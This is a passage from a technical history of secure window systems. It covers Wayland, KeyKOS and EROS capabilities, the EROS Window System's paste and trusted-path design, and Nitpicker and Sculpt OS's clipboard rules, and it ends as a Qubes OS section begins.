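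Wayland, which Kristian Høgsberg began in 2008, gives up compatibility with the X protocol. A single program, the compositor, acts as both display server and window manager. Each application draws its own windows in memory and passes the images to the compositor, which arranges them on the screen. The basic protocol has no request that lets a program read another program's window, watch its input or send it false keystrokes. The compositor sends keystrokes to the window that has keyboard focus, and it does not normally give programs the positions of their windows on the screen.

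Clipboard security improves less. Under the basic protocol, the compositor offers copied text only to the program with keyboard focus, so a background program cannot keep collecting it. But a program can read the clipboard as soon as the user switches to its window, even if the user never pastes. The EROS Window System had already gone further by tying each transfer to a user action.

People still need to take screenshots, share their screens and control computers remotely. The basic protocol leaves these jobs to the compositor. Some compositors, such as Sway, let ordinary programs capture the screen through an extension. GNOME and KDE, the two largest Linux desktops, mainly use portals, which are services outside the application that receive its request, usually ask the user, and return only what the user chose. In a video call, for example, the user can pick one window to share, and the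 meeting program receives images of only that window.

Portals protect best against programs in a sandbox, a restricted environment that blocks other routes to the same data. A program outside a sandbox runs with all the user's rights. Wayland may prevent it from reading a terminal's keystrokes, but it can still change the terminal's startup files so that the terminal runs the program's commands. A portal also cannot reliably identify a program outside a sandbox, so the permission dialog may show the wrong name.

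Wayland does not define a trusted path either. It has no secure attention key and does not require labels on windows, and a full-screen program can imitate the lock screen or a permission dialog. Protection against this, such as the key combination that systemd introduced in 2024, has to come from the compositor and the rest of the system.

The main desktops have nevertheless largely committed to Wayland. GNOME disabled its X11 session by default in September 2025 and removed it in version 50, in March 2026. KDE announced in November 2025 that its Plasma desktop would drop the X11 session in version 6.8. Xfce and Cinnamon, two smaller desktops, have moved more slowly. X applications still run on Wayland desktops through Xwayland, an X server that works as a client of the compositor. Xwayland keeps these applications from using X requests to read the windows of native Wayland programs, but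 applications that share an Xwayland server can still spy on one another.

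## Capabilities in KeyKOS and EROS

Most operating systems, including those that run Wayland desktops, decide what a program may do by checking whose account it runs under. In a capability system, a program starts with references to a few objects and can act only on those. The best-known argument for this design comes from an accident with a billing file.

### The confused deputy

In the late 1970s Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers, kept a compiler in a directory called SYSX. In the 1988 article *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy recalls what went wrong with it. A customer could run the compiler and name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also recorded which language features people used, in a file called (SYSX)STAT, so Tymshare gave it a licence to write to any file in SYSX. That directory also held the company's billing records, in a file called (SYSX)BILL.

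One customer learned that name and gave it as the destination for the debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file of that name for writing. The operating system allowed this because the compiler had a licence for SYSX, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Checking the file name would have been a poor fix. The compiler could have refused names in other directories, but customers had good reasons to send output there. It could have refused anything in SYSX, but that directory did not exist when the programmers wrote the code, and some people were entitled to write to it. It could have refused (SYSX)BILL, but then somebody would have had to change the compiler whenever another sensitive file appeared. The code had been correct until Tymshare added the licence. To see that the licence made it unsafe, someone would have had to examine every situation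 in which the compiler wrote a file.

Hardy calls the compiler a confused deputy because it acted on authority from two sources. It was supposed to use the customer's authority to write the debugging output and its own licence to write the statistics. But its request to the operating system contained only a file name, with no way to specify which authority to use, and the operating system accepted either. Tymshare added a system call that let a program "switch hats" to choose an authority. That would have stopped this attack, but some programs needed more than two authorities, and files were not the only things that needed protection. By Hardy's last count, the rule for opening a file contained fourteen "ands" and "ors".

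With capabilities, Tymshare would give the compiler a capability to the statistics file, and the customer would pass it a capability to the output file along with the request to compile. The compiler would write each kind of output through the matching capability. A customer who wanted to overwrite the billing records would first need a capability to them. A bug could still make the compiler mix up its two capabilities and corrupt the statistics, but the compiler could not access the billing records, because neither capability refers to them.

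The usual alternative is an access control list, which records the accounts that may use each file. In a table with a row for each user and a column for each file, an access control list is a column and a set of capabilities is a row, so textbooks often present the two methods as equivalent. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) objects that the table leaves out how programs refer to files and how permissions change. With lists, a program has to refer to a file by a name that carries no authority, which is how the compiler got confused. Lists also work best with a fairly stable set of accounts, so in practice they don't give two running copies of the same program different rights, as a capability system can.

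### How a program gets and uses a capability

Tymshare began work on the system that became KeyKOS in 1975. According to *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture*, by Bomberger, Frantz and colleagues, Tymshare wanted accurate accounting, uninterrupted service and protection for customers who did not trust one another. KeyKOS ran commercial applications from January 1983, and a new company, Key Logic, took over development in 1985. Jonathan Shapiro, who co-wrote the paper, later led the redesign of KeyKOS for ordinary PC processors as EROS.

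KeyKOS calls its capabilities keys. A program gets, holds and passes them as follows:

1. Whoever creates the program puts its first keys into numbered slots. In KeyKOS a running program has 16 general slots.
2. The kernel stores the slots outside the memory that the program can read or write. The program refers to a key only by its slot number.
3. To use an object, the program asks the kernel to send a message through, say, the key in slot 3. The kernel looks up the key and delivers the message to the object.
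4. The message can carry up to 4,096 bytes of data and up to four keys. The sender names the slots that hold the keys, and the kernel copies those keys to the recipient.
5. If the sender expects an answer, the kernel adds a key that the recipient can use to reply. The recipient gains no other authority over the sender.

A program can't make a key out of data because the system stores the two separately. Rajunas, Hardy and colleagues explain in *Security in KeyKOS* that pages hold only data and nodes hold only keys. Even if a program learned the exact bits of a key and wrote them into its memory, they would remain ordinary data, because no operation turns the contents of a page into a key. Guessing a slot number doesn't help either, because the number refers only to the program's own slots. Some other capability systems store data and capabilities together in memory, and the hardware marks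 each genuine capability with a tag that ordinary instructions can't set.

This separation resembles a parameterised query, which treats a customer's text only as a value. Text in the data part of a KeyKOS message can name any file without granting access to it.

### The confinement problem

Capabilities limit what a program can access, but a program that receives private data may still pass it on. In 1973 the computer scientist Butler Lampson asked how a customer could run someone else's program on private data and be sure the program would not leak it. He called this the confinement problem. In the KeyKOS version, one company owns a secret algorithm and another owns secret data. The data owner wants to run the algorithm without revealing the data to the algorithm's owner, who wants to sell the service without revealing the code.

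KeyKOS solves this with a trusted service called a factory. Hardy's 1986 patent, *Computer security system*, describes a builder who installs a program in a factory and then seals it, after which the builder can no longer alter the contents. Before running the program, the data owner asks the system to check the sealed factory. The system examines the keys that a new copy of the program would receive, but not the code. A key that would let the program write to something outside is a hole. For example, if the builder has included a key to their own storage, the program could save a copy of the data there, so the factory fails the check. If the factory passes, it builds the program in storage that belongs to the data owner.

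A confined program can still read shared material, such as a table of tax rates, but ordinary read-only access is not strict enough. A folder that the program can only read might contain a key that permits writing to a file, and the program could copy out that key and use it. KeyKOS therefore has sense keys, which weaken every key that a program fetches through them. EROS has the same mechanism, called weak capabilities. Anything obtained through a weak capability is itself weak and read-only, however many steps the program takes to reach it (Heiser 2002).

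The constructor is the EROS counterpart of the factory. It holds the program and its initial capabilities, and it can report to a client whether a new copy will have any outward channel that the client has not approved. If one of the initial capabilities leads to another constructor, so that the program can start helper programs, the check has to cover the helpers too. Shapiro (2005), answering a question on a mailing list, wrote that the EROS shell, which starts users' programs, ran the check all the time. Most other programs did not run it, because the shell's check already covered everything a program was built from.

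Shapiro and Sam Weber published a proof of the mechanism in 2000. Using a mathematical model of a broad class of capability systems that includes EROS, they showed that a program that passes a few checks before it starts will stay confined whatever its code does. A program can obtain a capability only by starting with it, creating a new object or receiving it through a capability that already connects it to the sender. A program that starts with no unapproved path out can therefore gain one only if someone outside who can reach it gives it a capability.

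The proof therefore depends on two starting conditions, which Shapiro, Smith and Farber give in slides on EROS: the client has exclusive access to the new program, and the program has no unauthorised channels. After that, the client controls all the program's communication, but can still make a mistake, such as handing the program a network connection. The proof also assumes that the kernel behaves like the model and that trusted services, such as the constructor and the storage allocator, work correctly. It covers only access through capabilities, so it does not rule out signals a program sends through timing.

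Shapiro said in 2005 that model checking of the real code had confirmed that EROS satisfied the formal model, although he conceded that bugs remained possible. He was defending his own system, but his comparison with Unix-like systems is fair, because their standard does not define correct behaviour completely enough to test such a claim.

### The save dialog

A confined text editor must still be able to save documents. On EROS, the editor starts without access to the user's files. When the user wants to save a letter, the editor calls a trusted program, the save agent, which holds a capability to the user's file system. The agent displays a save dialog, the user chooses a file, and the agent gives the editor a capability to that file alone.

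Suppose that the editor is malicious and draws a perfect copy of the save dialog. The user picks the file that holds their tax return and clicks Save. The editor gets the file's name, but the name doesn't give it a capability to open the file. It can falsely report that it saved the letter, which it could have done anyway. Shapiro and colleagues conclude that the save dialog needs no trusted path. The protection comes from the capabilities that the genuine dialog holds, so it works even if the user cannot tell the genuine dialog from a fake.

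They argue that in a system built this way, only password prompts, prompts for the passphrases that unlock cryptographic keys, and login still need a trusted path. In each case the user types something valuable to whoever receives it, as with a credential prompt in Windows. The window system built on EROS has special protection for these three cases.

The list should probably also require the dialog to show which program will receive the file, and the display server to prevent other programs from covering or imitating that information. Otherwise, a malicious game could request the genuine file dialog while the user is working in a word processor. If the dialog appears over the word processor's window, the user may choose a letter, believing that the word processor requested it, and the game will receive the letter.

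### Powerboxes and Yee's rules

Engineers call a trusted file chooser of this kind a powerbox. CapDesk, an experimental desktop, used one to give applications access to individual files. Researchers at Hewlett-Packard then brought the idea to Windows XP in a package called Polaris, which changed neither Windows nor the applications.

Polaris starts a program such as Excel in a separate user account that has almost no permissions. When the user double-clicks a spreadsheet, Polaris copies the file into a folder that this account can use and keeps the copy and the original synchronized. If the user later chooses Open from the File menu, Polaris detects Excel's dialog and replaces it with its own, which has access to all the user's files. Excel gets access only to the file that the user picks. A virus hidden in the spreadsheet can damage that spreadsheet, but it can't search the disk for other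 documents or install itself in the startup folder.

About 25 people at Hewlett-Packard and some outsiders used the first test version from June 2005. Most of them hardly noticed it, and one executive used it for several days before the researchers told him they had installed it. The developers also reported that viruses had run in protected programs without harming anything else. These results are encouraging, but the trial was small and the developers evaluated their own work. The program did not limit network access, so a virus could still send the open document to a stranger. It also worked badly with spreadsheets that refer to other spreadsheets, because the user had chosen only the first one.

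With a powerbox, the user's ordinary choice of a file also gives the program permission to use it. With a conventional prompt, the user chooses a file and then has to decide separately whether the program may open it. Yee (2004), in *Aligning Security and Usability*, recommends that systems infer authorisation from such acts of designation. His later guidelines, as listed by the publisher O'Reilly, begin with two related rules. The most comfortable way to do a task should also grant the least authority, and a system should grant authority to others only in accordance with user actions that show consent.

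Ka-Ping Yee developed his ideas partly through years of contact with the EROS community, and Shapiro's team included features in their window system to support his ideas. Yee's earlier set of ten principles, which Weinhold (2007) summarises in *User Interaction Design for Secure Systems*, also says that users should be able to see and revoke authority. The set includes a trusted path, so Yee did not expect powerboxes to replace one. Powerboxes work well when the user's action identifies one object. They help less with a backup program, which needs every file, or with a task whose files the user can't name in advance.

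### Revocation, leaks and speed

Access granted through a capability can be taken back, though critics have long argued otherwise. Miller and colleagues accept that the person who grants a capability cannot remove it from the program that holds it, but they show how to cut off access anyway. Suppose Alice wants to let Bob use a file for a week. She gives him a capability to a forwarder, a small program that passes his requests to the file, and she keeps the means of switching it off. After she switches it off at the end of the week, Bob still has his capability, but neither it nor any copy he gave to others reaches the file.

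In *Paradigm Regained*, Miller and Shapiro trace the mistake to formal studies that looked only at who held which permissions and ignored what programs such as the forwarder could do. Rajunas and colleagues had already acknowledged a limit to the reply. If the object behind the forwarder can send capabilities back through it, Bob may obtain a direct capability that bypasses the switch. The forwarder must then inspect or replace the capabilities that pass through it. Revocation also cannot retrieve data that Bob has already copied.

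Covert channels are a harder problem. KeyKOS programs share nothing by default, which removes many of the usual channels, but Rajunas and colleagues list several that depend on timing. For example, a program can measure how long a shared page takes to load and work out whether another program has used it recently. The researchers argue that other activity on the machine tends to obscure such signals, and that giving each program an artificial clock would close these channels. This noise is a weak defence, since a sender can repeat each bit until the receiver gets it. Artificial clocks would be more effective, but KeyKOS didn't have them, and many programs need the real time.

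Capability systems also had a reputation for being slow. Shapiro, Smith and Farber (1999) responded in *EROS* by measuring basic operations on EROS and Linux. On a 400 MHz Pentium II, EROS created a process in 0.66 milliseconds and Linux in 1.92, but the simplest system call took 1.6 microseconds on EROS and 0.7 on Linux. These tests show that capabilities do not have to make a kernel slow, but not how fast a full set of applications would run on EROS, which never had one.

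### Old software and what survives

Existing programs are written to open any file by name, which a pure capability system doesn't allow. KeyKOS supported them by running whole operating systems, including a version of Unix, on top of its kernel, and it kept these systems separate from one another. But programs inside the same copy of Unix had the usual Unix permissions, so a confused deputy there was as dangerous as before. EROS had less software, and in 2004 its developers were still struggling to get commonly used applications running. This probably limited its use more than any weakness in its security.

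Hardy thought capabilities had to be the foundation of a system, because some systems that added them to older mechanisms ended up with the disadvantages of both. Later projects have had more success with such mixtures than he expected. Capsicum, which is part of FreeBSD, lets a Unix program enter a mode in which it can no longer open files by name. From then on, it can use only the open files and connections it already holds or receives from another program. Programmers can convert one application at a time, but each conversion takes work, and unconverted programs keep all their old permissions.

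Pure capability kernels also survive, mostly outside desktop computing. CapROS, led by the KeyKOS developer Charles Landau, continues EROS directly. The seL4 kernel, from a different family, controls access through capabilities and has a machine-checked proof that its code matches its specification. Google shipped Fuchsia, another capability-based system, on its Nest Hub displays in 2021. CHERI, a research design for processors, brings back hardware tags so that even a pointer inside a program can be a capability the program can't forge.

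More people have used a powerbox than any of these kernels. On a Mac, a sandboxed application gains access to a document when the user picks it in the system's Open or Save panel. File portals on Linux desktops work in much the same way.

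## The EROS Window System and Nitpicker

A powerbox treats the user's choice of a file as permission for a program to open it. Shapiro's team applied similar reasoning to the clipboard in the EROS Window System (EWS), a display server they wrote from scratch for EROS and described in 2004. They wanted to keep overlapping windows, cut and paste, and drag and drop because users expected them. X lets programs interact freely, but EWS isolates them completely by default and lets two programs communicate only when the user's action requires it.

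A year later, Norman Feske and Christian Helmuth, two researchers in Dresden, published Nitpicker, a display server about a third the size. It is still part of a working desktop system.

### Nine goals for a display server

Volitional traceability is the most important of the nine goals that Shapiro and colleagues set for EWS. Unlike X, EWS may transfer data between applications only if its developers can show that a particular keystroke or mouse action by the user authorised the transfer.

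Three related goals limit contact between clients. One client's operations should not affect another client or reveal anything about it. The server should not hold data that several clients can change, and it should let clients communicate only as needed for familiar actions such as pasting.

To be easier to check, the server should also manage few types of resource, avoid complicated algorithms and be small enough for evaluators to examine.

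The last two goals concern memory and time. The server should not queue requests, and it should limit its own memory use; any extra memory should come from the client that needs it. It should also deliver each input event to only one program and finish every operation in a short, fixed time. These rules help with speed, and they also limit covert channels, since one program could otherwise signal to another by slowing down the other's requests.

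EWS falls short of its goals in three ways. A paste requires messages to two programs instead of one. Closing a session also closes any sessions nested inside it, so one client can affect another. The server keeps window records in its own memory rather than the client's, so that memory can be exhausted.

### How input reaches a program

The EWS display server controls the screen memory and the input devices. Each input device has a small helper process that waits for its input. When the user presses a key, the keyboard helper converts the hardware signal into a standard form and calls the server to report it. Applications also call the server, but they hold different capabilities to it than the helpers do, so their requests arrive through a separate interface.

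An application therefore cannot send false keystrokes to another program, as an X client can. It would need the capability that the keyboard helper uses to report events, and it cannot use its own capability for this. EWS can thus guarantee that input came from the user, as long as the server, the helper and the hardware are sound. A compromised keyboard helper could still invent keystrokes. Supporting a new device mostly requires a new helper, which runs outside the server's memory, so evaluators would not have to examine the whole server again.

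The server handles each request immediately and adds any resulting event to a short list for the program that should receive it. A mouse event normally goes to the program whose window is under the pointer. While the user holds down a mouse button, the window where they pressed it receives all mouse events, even if the pointer leaves that window.

If a program asks for its next event and there isn't one, the server makes the program wait in a queue inside the EROS kernel, which later wakes it according to the operating system's scheduling rules. X's server keeps its own queue of requests and usually has no access to the system's priorities. Revealing priority changes to programs would not be a safe solution, because one program could then signal to another by causing such changes.

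### Sessions that hide events from their parents

A program creates its windows and receives their events through a capability called a session. Holding the capability is enough, so the display server doesn't check the program's identity. Sessions can also be nested. A desktop shell, for example, can provide a window in which a mail program creates its own windows. Although the mail program appears to be inside the shell, the shell can't access its input.

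To set this up, the shell requests a *session creator*, a capability for making sessions inside one of the shell's windows, and gives it to the mail program. The mail program can check that the capability leads to the real display server rather than an imitation provided by the shell. It then uses the session creator to make its own session. The shell never holds the capability for that session, so it cannot read the mail program's events or add a deceptive window to the session. The shell can still end the mail program's session by destroying the shell's own session.

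Each user account also has its own running copy of EWS. A trusted program connects that copy to the screen and input devices when the user logs in and disconnects it when the user logs out. EROS preserves running programs across restarts, so the user's windows and sessions remain in place while the user is away.

### Drawing in shared memory

An X program sends the server drawing instructions, such as a request to draw a polygon. The server needs a lot of code to carry these out, and some take far longer than others. In EWS, each program draws its own windows in memory it shares with the server, which can read that memory but not change it. When the program changes part of a window, it tells the server which rectangle to update, and the server copies those pixels to the screen. Wayland later divided the work in much the same way.

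This leaves the server with only two drawing operations, copying a block of pixels and filling a rectangle. It also removes the covert channel that X's redraw notices create. When one EWS window moves off another, the server already has the picture underneath, so it can display it without notifying the program that drew it.

Shared memory introduces a new problem because a client program can withdraw the memory while the server is copying from it. Only one routine in the server reads clients' memory, and it catches the resulting error. The server then ends the client's session. A client could use this to detect that the server was copying its window at a particular moment, but only once before losing its session.

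Programs now need their own drawing and font code, which X used to provide. Shapiro and colleagues do not consider the drawing library a substantial new threat, because applications already depend on large libraries for their menus and buttons. They worry more about fonts, which several applications are likely to share. A distributor could supply a font in which one character looks like another, and the researchers know of no way to prevent this. EROS can at least stop anyone from changing a font after installation.

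### One paste, step by step

A paste from the keyboard is easy to trace because the server receives the actual keystroke from the keyboard helper and has a table of keystrokes that conventionally mean cut or paste, such as Ctrl+V.

Mouse pastes are harder to verify because when someone clicks Paste in a menu, the server receives only the position of the click. The application drew the menu, so only the application can report that the click landed on Paste, and a hostile application could make the same claim about any click. Shapiro's team considered moving all menus into the server but decided against it because it would have made the server more complicated, restricted application designers and required large changes to existing toolkits.

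EWS instead requires an application to mark the areas where a click means cut or paste. It does this with a special invisible window that accepts no input itself. Suppose a user has copied a diagram from an unclassified drawing program and wants to paste it into a secret report, and that the security rules permit this:

1. The report editor draws its menu and places an invisible paste window over the Paste item.
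2. The user moves the pointer to Paste. The server replaces the usual cursor with a distinctive one that always means paste.
3. The user clicks, and the click passes through the invisible window to the menu. When the user releases the button, the server treats this as permission to paste, provided that the distinctive cursor has been visible for a minimum time.
4. The server looks up which window supplied the copied material and checks that the rules allow a transfer from that session to the editor's.
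5. The server creates an empty region of memory for the diagram, using a constructor that the drawing program supplied. It gives the drawing program a capability to the region.
6. The drawing program writes the diagram into the region in its own format. It also provides a constructor for a converter, a program that can translate the diagram into other formats.
7. The server freezes the region so that neither program can change it.
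8. The server gives the editor capabilities to the frozen region and the converter's constructor. The editor starts the converter, asks which formats it can produce and requests one that it can use.

Step 3 requires a minimum time because a program might move its paste windows around at random and catch a click meant for something else before the user had time to notice the cursor. Shapiro and colleagues do not give a figure for the delay.

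The converter lets a secret recipient choose a data format without replying to the program that supplies the data. Normally that program offers a list of formats, and the recipient replies with the ones it wants. Here, the reply would carry information from the secret editor to the unclassified drawing program, so in EWS the editor negotiates with the converter instead. The converter's code comes from the drawing program's side, but EROS can confirm through the constructor that the running converter cannot send anything out. The converter also runs in storage that the editor provides.

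The team uses one confined converter that handles all the formats. Passing the editor a list of converters, one for each format, would be unsafe because the sender could replace an entry with a capability to something else after the server had checked it.

Shapiro's team claim that this arrangement leaves no channel from the recipient back to the sender, but they describe one in a footnote. The frozen region occupies the sender's storage, so the sender can detect when the recipient deletes it, and a hostile recipient could signal through the timing of deletions. The team planned to transfer ownership of the storage during the paste and immediately give the sender equivalent space, which would hide the deletion. Until that change is made, the sender can also reclaim the region at any time, so a recipient that needs the diagram for long should make a copy.

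A more practical weakness is that the server can verify that the user clicked in an area marked for pasting, but not that the user meant to paste. A game could put a paste window over its Play button and receive the clipboard's contents when the user clicked. The only warning would be an unusual cursor, and the experiments on browser indicators suggest that many people would miss it. EWS still improves on X, because the game needs a click for each paste and cannot monitor the clipboard in the background.

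Normally, the window where the user presses the mouse button receives all mouse events until the release. Drag and drop needs an exception to this rule, so the source program can mark a movement as a drag. The server then notifies each window the pointer crosses, but only if that window is allowed to receive the data. When the user releases the button, the server notifies both the source and the destination. Two programs could encode a message in these events, but no faster than the user moves the mouse.

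### Why any border label can be forged

The compartmented mode requirements call for a security label on each window. Shapiro and colleagues argue that this is not enough, because an application can imitate any label the server draws on a border. For example, an unclassified program can open a large window and paint a smaller one inside it, with a title bar and a "Secret" label. The user appears to have two windows open, one unclassified and one secret, but both belong to the unclassified program.

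Dimming the windows without keyboard focus does not help by itself. The program can darken its own picture around the false window with the server's formula, so that the false window seems to have the focus.

EWS combines dimming with a prominent, brightly coloured border around the window that really has the focus. In the example, the unclassified program can darken its picture but not the border that the server draws around it, so the bright border still shows that the larger window is receiving the keystrokes. The designers chose a bright colour because people notice dimming less easily in dark ones. The server also reserves a band at the bottom of the screen for label information. Qubes OS also draws coloured borders, which identify the virtual machine that owns each window.

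EWS treats a click on the minimise button as an order from the user, so the server draws the title bar and minimises the window itself instead of asking the application to do it. Applications can supply the text of the title, but EWS always displays it in a single font built into the server. A program that supplied its own font could send the server one title and make the letters appear as another.

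A program might also try to cover another program's button with a transparent window and intercept the click. EWS does not let an invisible window receive input, but a nearly transparent one can, and it looks much the same. The server reduces this risk by requiring borders on all top-level windows, though Shapiro's team acknowledges that borders do not eliminate it.

### The prompts that still need a trusted path

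An attacker gains nothing by faking a save dialog on EROS, but can still steal a password, key passphrase or login details by faking the prompt for them.

Because there are only three such cases, Shapiro and colleagues consider it reasonable to handle them with a few trusted programs. EWS gives these programs a special kind of session. When one of their windows is active, the server tints every other window red and marks the reserved band at the bottom of the screen. The server does not have to verify the text in their prompts because it can rely on these programs to identify themselves correctly.

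Suppose an accounting program must confirm the user's password before it displays the payroll. It starts a copy of the trusted password checker and supplies a username. The checker opens its prompt, the rest of the screen turns red, and the user types the password. The accounting program receives only true or false. A similar service handles cryptographic keys without revealing the decrypted keys to the programs that use it.

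A malicious program can still draw a false password prompt and tint the rest of its own window red. It can't tint other programs' windows or mark the reserved band, but if its window fills most of the screen, the band and the border may be the only visible differences. The protection then depends on the user checking them before typing. Shapiro's team say that they had concentrated on separating programs and that how the trusted path is presented needed more study. They do not describe a secure attention key, which would let a suspicious user summon the real prompt.

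### What the prototype established

The EWS prototype has fewer than 4,500 lines of code, including drivers for two kinds of display hardware. Shapiro and colleagues put this at 2 to 5 percent of the code in X11. The comparison is uneven because EWS leaves network connections and most drawing to other programs. Keeping that drawing code outside the trusted computing base is also the main advantage of the design, since a fault in one application's drawing code should not expose another application's windows.

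The team also say that users would notice no reduction in functionality. This is harder to accept because EROS did not yet run most commonly used applications, and a conversion of the Gtk graphics toolkit was still in progress. They had not tuned the server for speed, but they reported no noticeable delays when using it for presentations to DARPA.

A comparison with DOpE, a real-time window system that Feske and Hermann Härtig wrote at TU Dresden, supports the decision to keep the server simple. DOpE has 7,000 lines of core code and drivers, and another 3,000 for its more elaborate widgets (interface parts such as buttons and menus). Its core is 2,500 lines larger than that of EWS, and Shapiro's team attribute most of the difference to simpler widgets built into DOpE's core. By that estimate, DOpE's widgets take up about 5,500 lines, more than all of EWS.

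The prototype lacked some of the planned security. The design attaches security labels to sessions and checks a rule before each transfer, but the prototype's rule allowed every transfer. In the example of the secret report, the check would have approved a paste in either direction. A separate process could supply a proper rule for several parts of the system to share. The team had not yet decided how to show different security levels on the screen.

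A hostile program could also open windows until the display server ran out of memory. The team planned to limit the total, perhaps to 65,536 windows, and to reserve some for trusted programs. A trusted monitor would then warn the user and offer to close the offending application. The prototype had none of these safeguards. A limit on the total would still allow covert signalling, because one program could use up the remaining windows and another could detect that it could not open any. Preventing this would require a separate quota for each client. The researchers suspected that EWS had less covert-channel capacity than X11, but did not try to prove it.

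The only usability test had one participant, four-year-old Wesley Vanderburgh, who used a paint program while his father, one of the paper's co-authors, observed. The researchers describe the test with obvious humour and call it inconclusive. It does not show whether people notice the paste cursor or know what a red screen means, and the security of EWS depends partly on both.

### Nitpicker's smaller server

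Feske and Helmuth's alternative, presented in *A Nitpicker's guide to a minimal-complexity secure GUI* (2005), is in effect a criticism of how much EWS still does inside trusted code. The EWS server draws title bars and borders, manages windows and directs the paste protocol. It also needs applications written for its own interface, and EROS had few of them. Feske and Helmuth moved window handling into the clients and designed the system to support existing software. Genode Labs, which now develops Nitpicker, puts the server at 1,500 lines on its page *Graphical User Interfaces*.

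Nitpicker is based on buffers and views. A buffer is memory that a client draws in, and a view is a rectangle on the screen that displays part of a buffer. One buffer can have several views, so a word processor might draw a document and a toolbar in different parts of one buffer and display them at different places on the screen. Clients also draw their own title bars, if they have them. The server only tracks the rectangles, copies the visible pixels to the screen and delivers input to the right client.

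This arrangement makes it fairly easy to support an existing window system. An ordinary X server can run as one client of Nitpicker and draw all its windows into one buffer. A small program can then track the position of each X window and create a matching view, so X applications appear on screen beside protected ones. Genode Labs describe several window systems sharing a screen in this way while staying completely isolated from one another.

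Nitpicker isolates window systems from each other but not the applications inside each one, so keeping a bank's program apart from a game requires a second X server, as in Trusted X. Nitpicker's users can divide their programs as they like, whereas Trusted X follows government classification levels.

Clients draw their own borders in this design, so a border does not reliably show which client a window belongs to. The Nitpicker server therefore draws labels over the clients' pictures, placing them so that they stay readable when another view partly covers the labelled one. Nitpicker later had an *X-ray mode* that tinted and labelled every view when the user pressed a reserved key. A false window that a program had painted inside its real one did not get its own label, because the server had no view for it.

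X-ray mode works a little like a secure attention key. The user presses a key that the server intercepts, so a program cannot avoid inspection by drawing a better imitation. But the user has to suspect something before pressing the key, and a screen under Nitpicker may show no security labels until then, whereas EWS always marks the focused window.

### Nitpicker in Genode

Feske and Helmuth later started Genode, a toolkit for building operating systems from small, isolated components. They kept Nitpicker but dropped DOpE. In a message to a TU Dresden mailing list, Feske explained that DOpE offered too little compared with established toolkits such as Qt4 and was quite complex.

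Genode also deals with the memory problem that EWS left unsolved. When a client opens a session with a server, it contributes memory from its own allowance, and the server uses that memory for the client's data. A program that creates thousands of views in Nitpicker therefore uses up only its own allowance.

Genode's developers later removed X-ray mode from Nitpicker. In a post to the Genode mailing list, Feske wrote that the mode's built-in rules had become an obstacle to more advanced desktops. He wanted, for example, to activate the mode whenever the pointer moved over a window's border, and to leave labels off trusted parts of the screen. Adding every such option would have made Nitpicker more complex without covering every case. One component now decides when X-ray mode is on, and another changes Nitpicker's settings to match.

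This keeps the central server simple, but the complete labelling mechanism now depends on more components and on their configuration. The basic configuration that Feske offers in the same post shows clients' pictures without tints or labels, which suits a demonstration but doesn't help the user detect a fake. In contrast, Mag, the display server of the related operating system framework L4Re, is a simple copy of Nitpicker that still has X-ray mode built in, with labels, coloured frames and a highlight around the session that has the input focus.

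Most Nitpicker users today run it through Sculpt OS, Genode's desktop system. Feske (2026) explains in *Sculpt Operating System 26.04* that a user who installs a program also decides which services it may use. A normal application connects to a window manager. Other options let a component draw the desktop background, act as a lock screen or connect directly to Nitpicker. Only one component, usually the window manager, may control keyboard focus, whereas in X any client can take over the keyboard.

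The user can press F12 at any time to switch between the desktop and Sculpt's administrative screen, which includes a diagram of the running components. Clicking on a component shows everything it relies on, so the user can confirm, for instance, that a command shell has no connection to the network. The diagram is more informative than a permission prompt, but the user has to understand it.

The window manager runs as a separate component between Nitpicker and the applications. Feske (2020), in *Compartmentalized window management in Sculpt OS*, describes one that can remember window positions and change the style of window borders while the windows are open. Applications that use this window manager have to trust it as well as Nitpicker, so Nitpicker's 1,500 lines are only part of the code that protects a typical desktop program. One of Sculpt's ready-made configurations divides the work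 further and, as Feske notes in the Sculpt manual, lets the user independently update or restart the component that draws window borders.

The project is still active. Genode's *Sculpt OS release 26.10* (2026) announced the first version of Sculpt to use a microkernel that Genode's developers wrote themselves.

### A clipboard with a time limit

Sculpt had no shared clipboard until July 2019, when Genode's *Sculpt OS release 19.07* (2019) introduced copy and paste between terminals, virtual machines and graphical applications. Feske (2019), in *Copy and paste with Sculpt OS 19.07*, explains that he did not want software as complex as a web browser to have access to his personal notes. He considered the Qubes OS method, which requires extra keystrokes to move text between virtual machines, but found it inconvenient, especially for people who copy and paste with the mouse.

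Feske observed that a legitimate use of the clipboard always follows a key press or mouse click in the application concerned. Sculpt therefore lets an application copy or paste only if the user has pressed a key or button in it during the previous 500 milliseconds. Nitpicker sends the clipboard the identity of the focused application and whether the user is interacting with it. The clipboard matches that identity against the requesting application's label, which the application cannot forge. If the labels don't match because somebody connected the application to the clipboard incorrectly, the clipboard refuses all its requests.

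This stops a background program from reading or replacing what the user has copied. Two cooperating programs could still use the clipboard to exchange secrets, but only as fast as the user switches between them. The rule also works with menus, keyboard shortcuts and terminal commands, and applications do not have to mark special areas on the screen as they do in EWS.

The evidence of consent is weaker than in EWS, however, because any key press counts, not just one that means paste. If the user copies a password from a password manager and then types a search into a browser, the browser can read the password within half a second of each keystroke, even if the user never pastes it. EWS would give the browser the password only after Ctrl+V or a click in a marked area, with the paste cursor showing. Sculpt's rule is easier for application developers, but it protects copied text only from programs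 that the user is not using.

Administrators can add fixed rules about which groups of programs may exchange data. Sculpt normally puts applications in one group and its administrative interface in another, and allows copying in both directions. A more cautious user could allow copying only from the applications to the administrative interface.

Neither kind of rule checks what the text contains, so a shell can run a stranger's text as a command even when the user authorised the paste. In an attack known as pastejacking, a web page puts a hidden command on the clipboard instead of the harmless text that the user selected. Feske warns that Sculpt's terminal does not protect against this and advises users not to paste from a browser directly into a command shell.

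## Qubes OS

EROS never had a full set of applications, and Genode users still have to learn an unusual system. Qubes OS runs ordinary Linux and Windows programs without fixing their bugs. It puts each area of the user's work in its own virtual machine, or qube, which is a simulated computer with a separate operating system and files. A hypervisor, a layer of software that runs directly on the hardware, keeps the qubes apart, and a privileged virtual machine called dom0 shows all their windows on one desktop.

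### Why virtual machines

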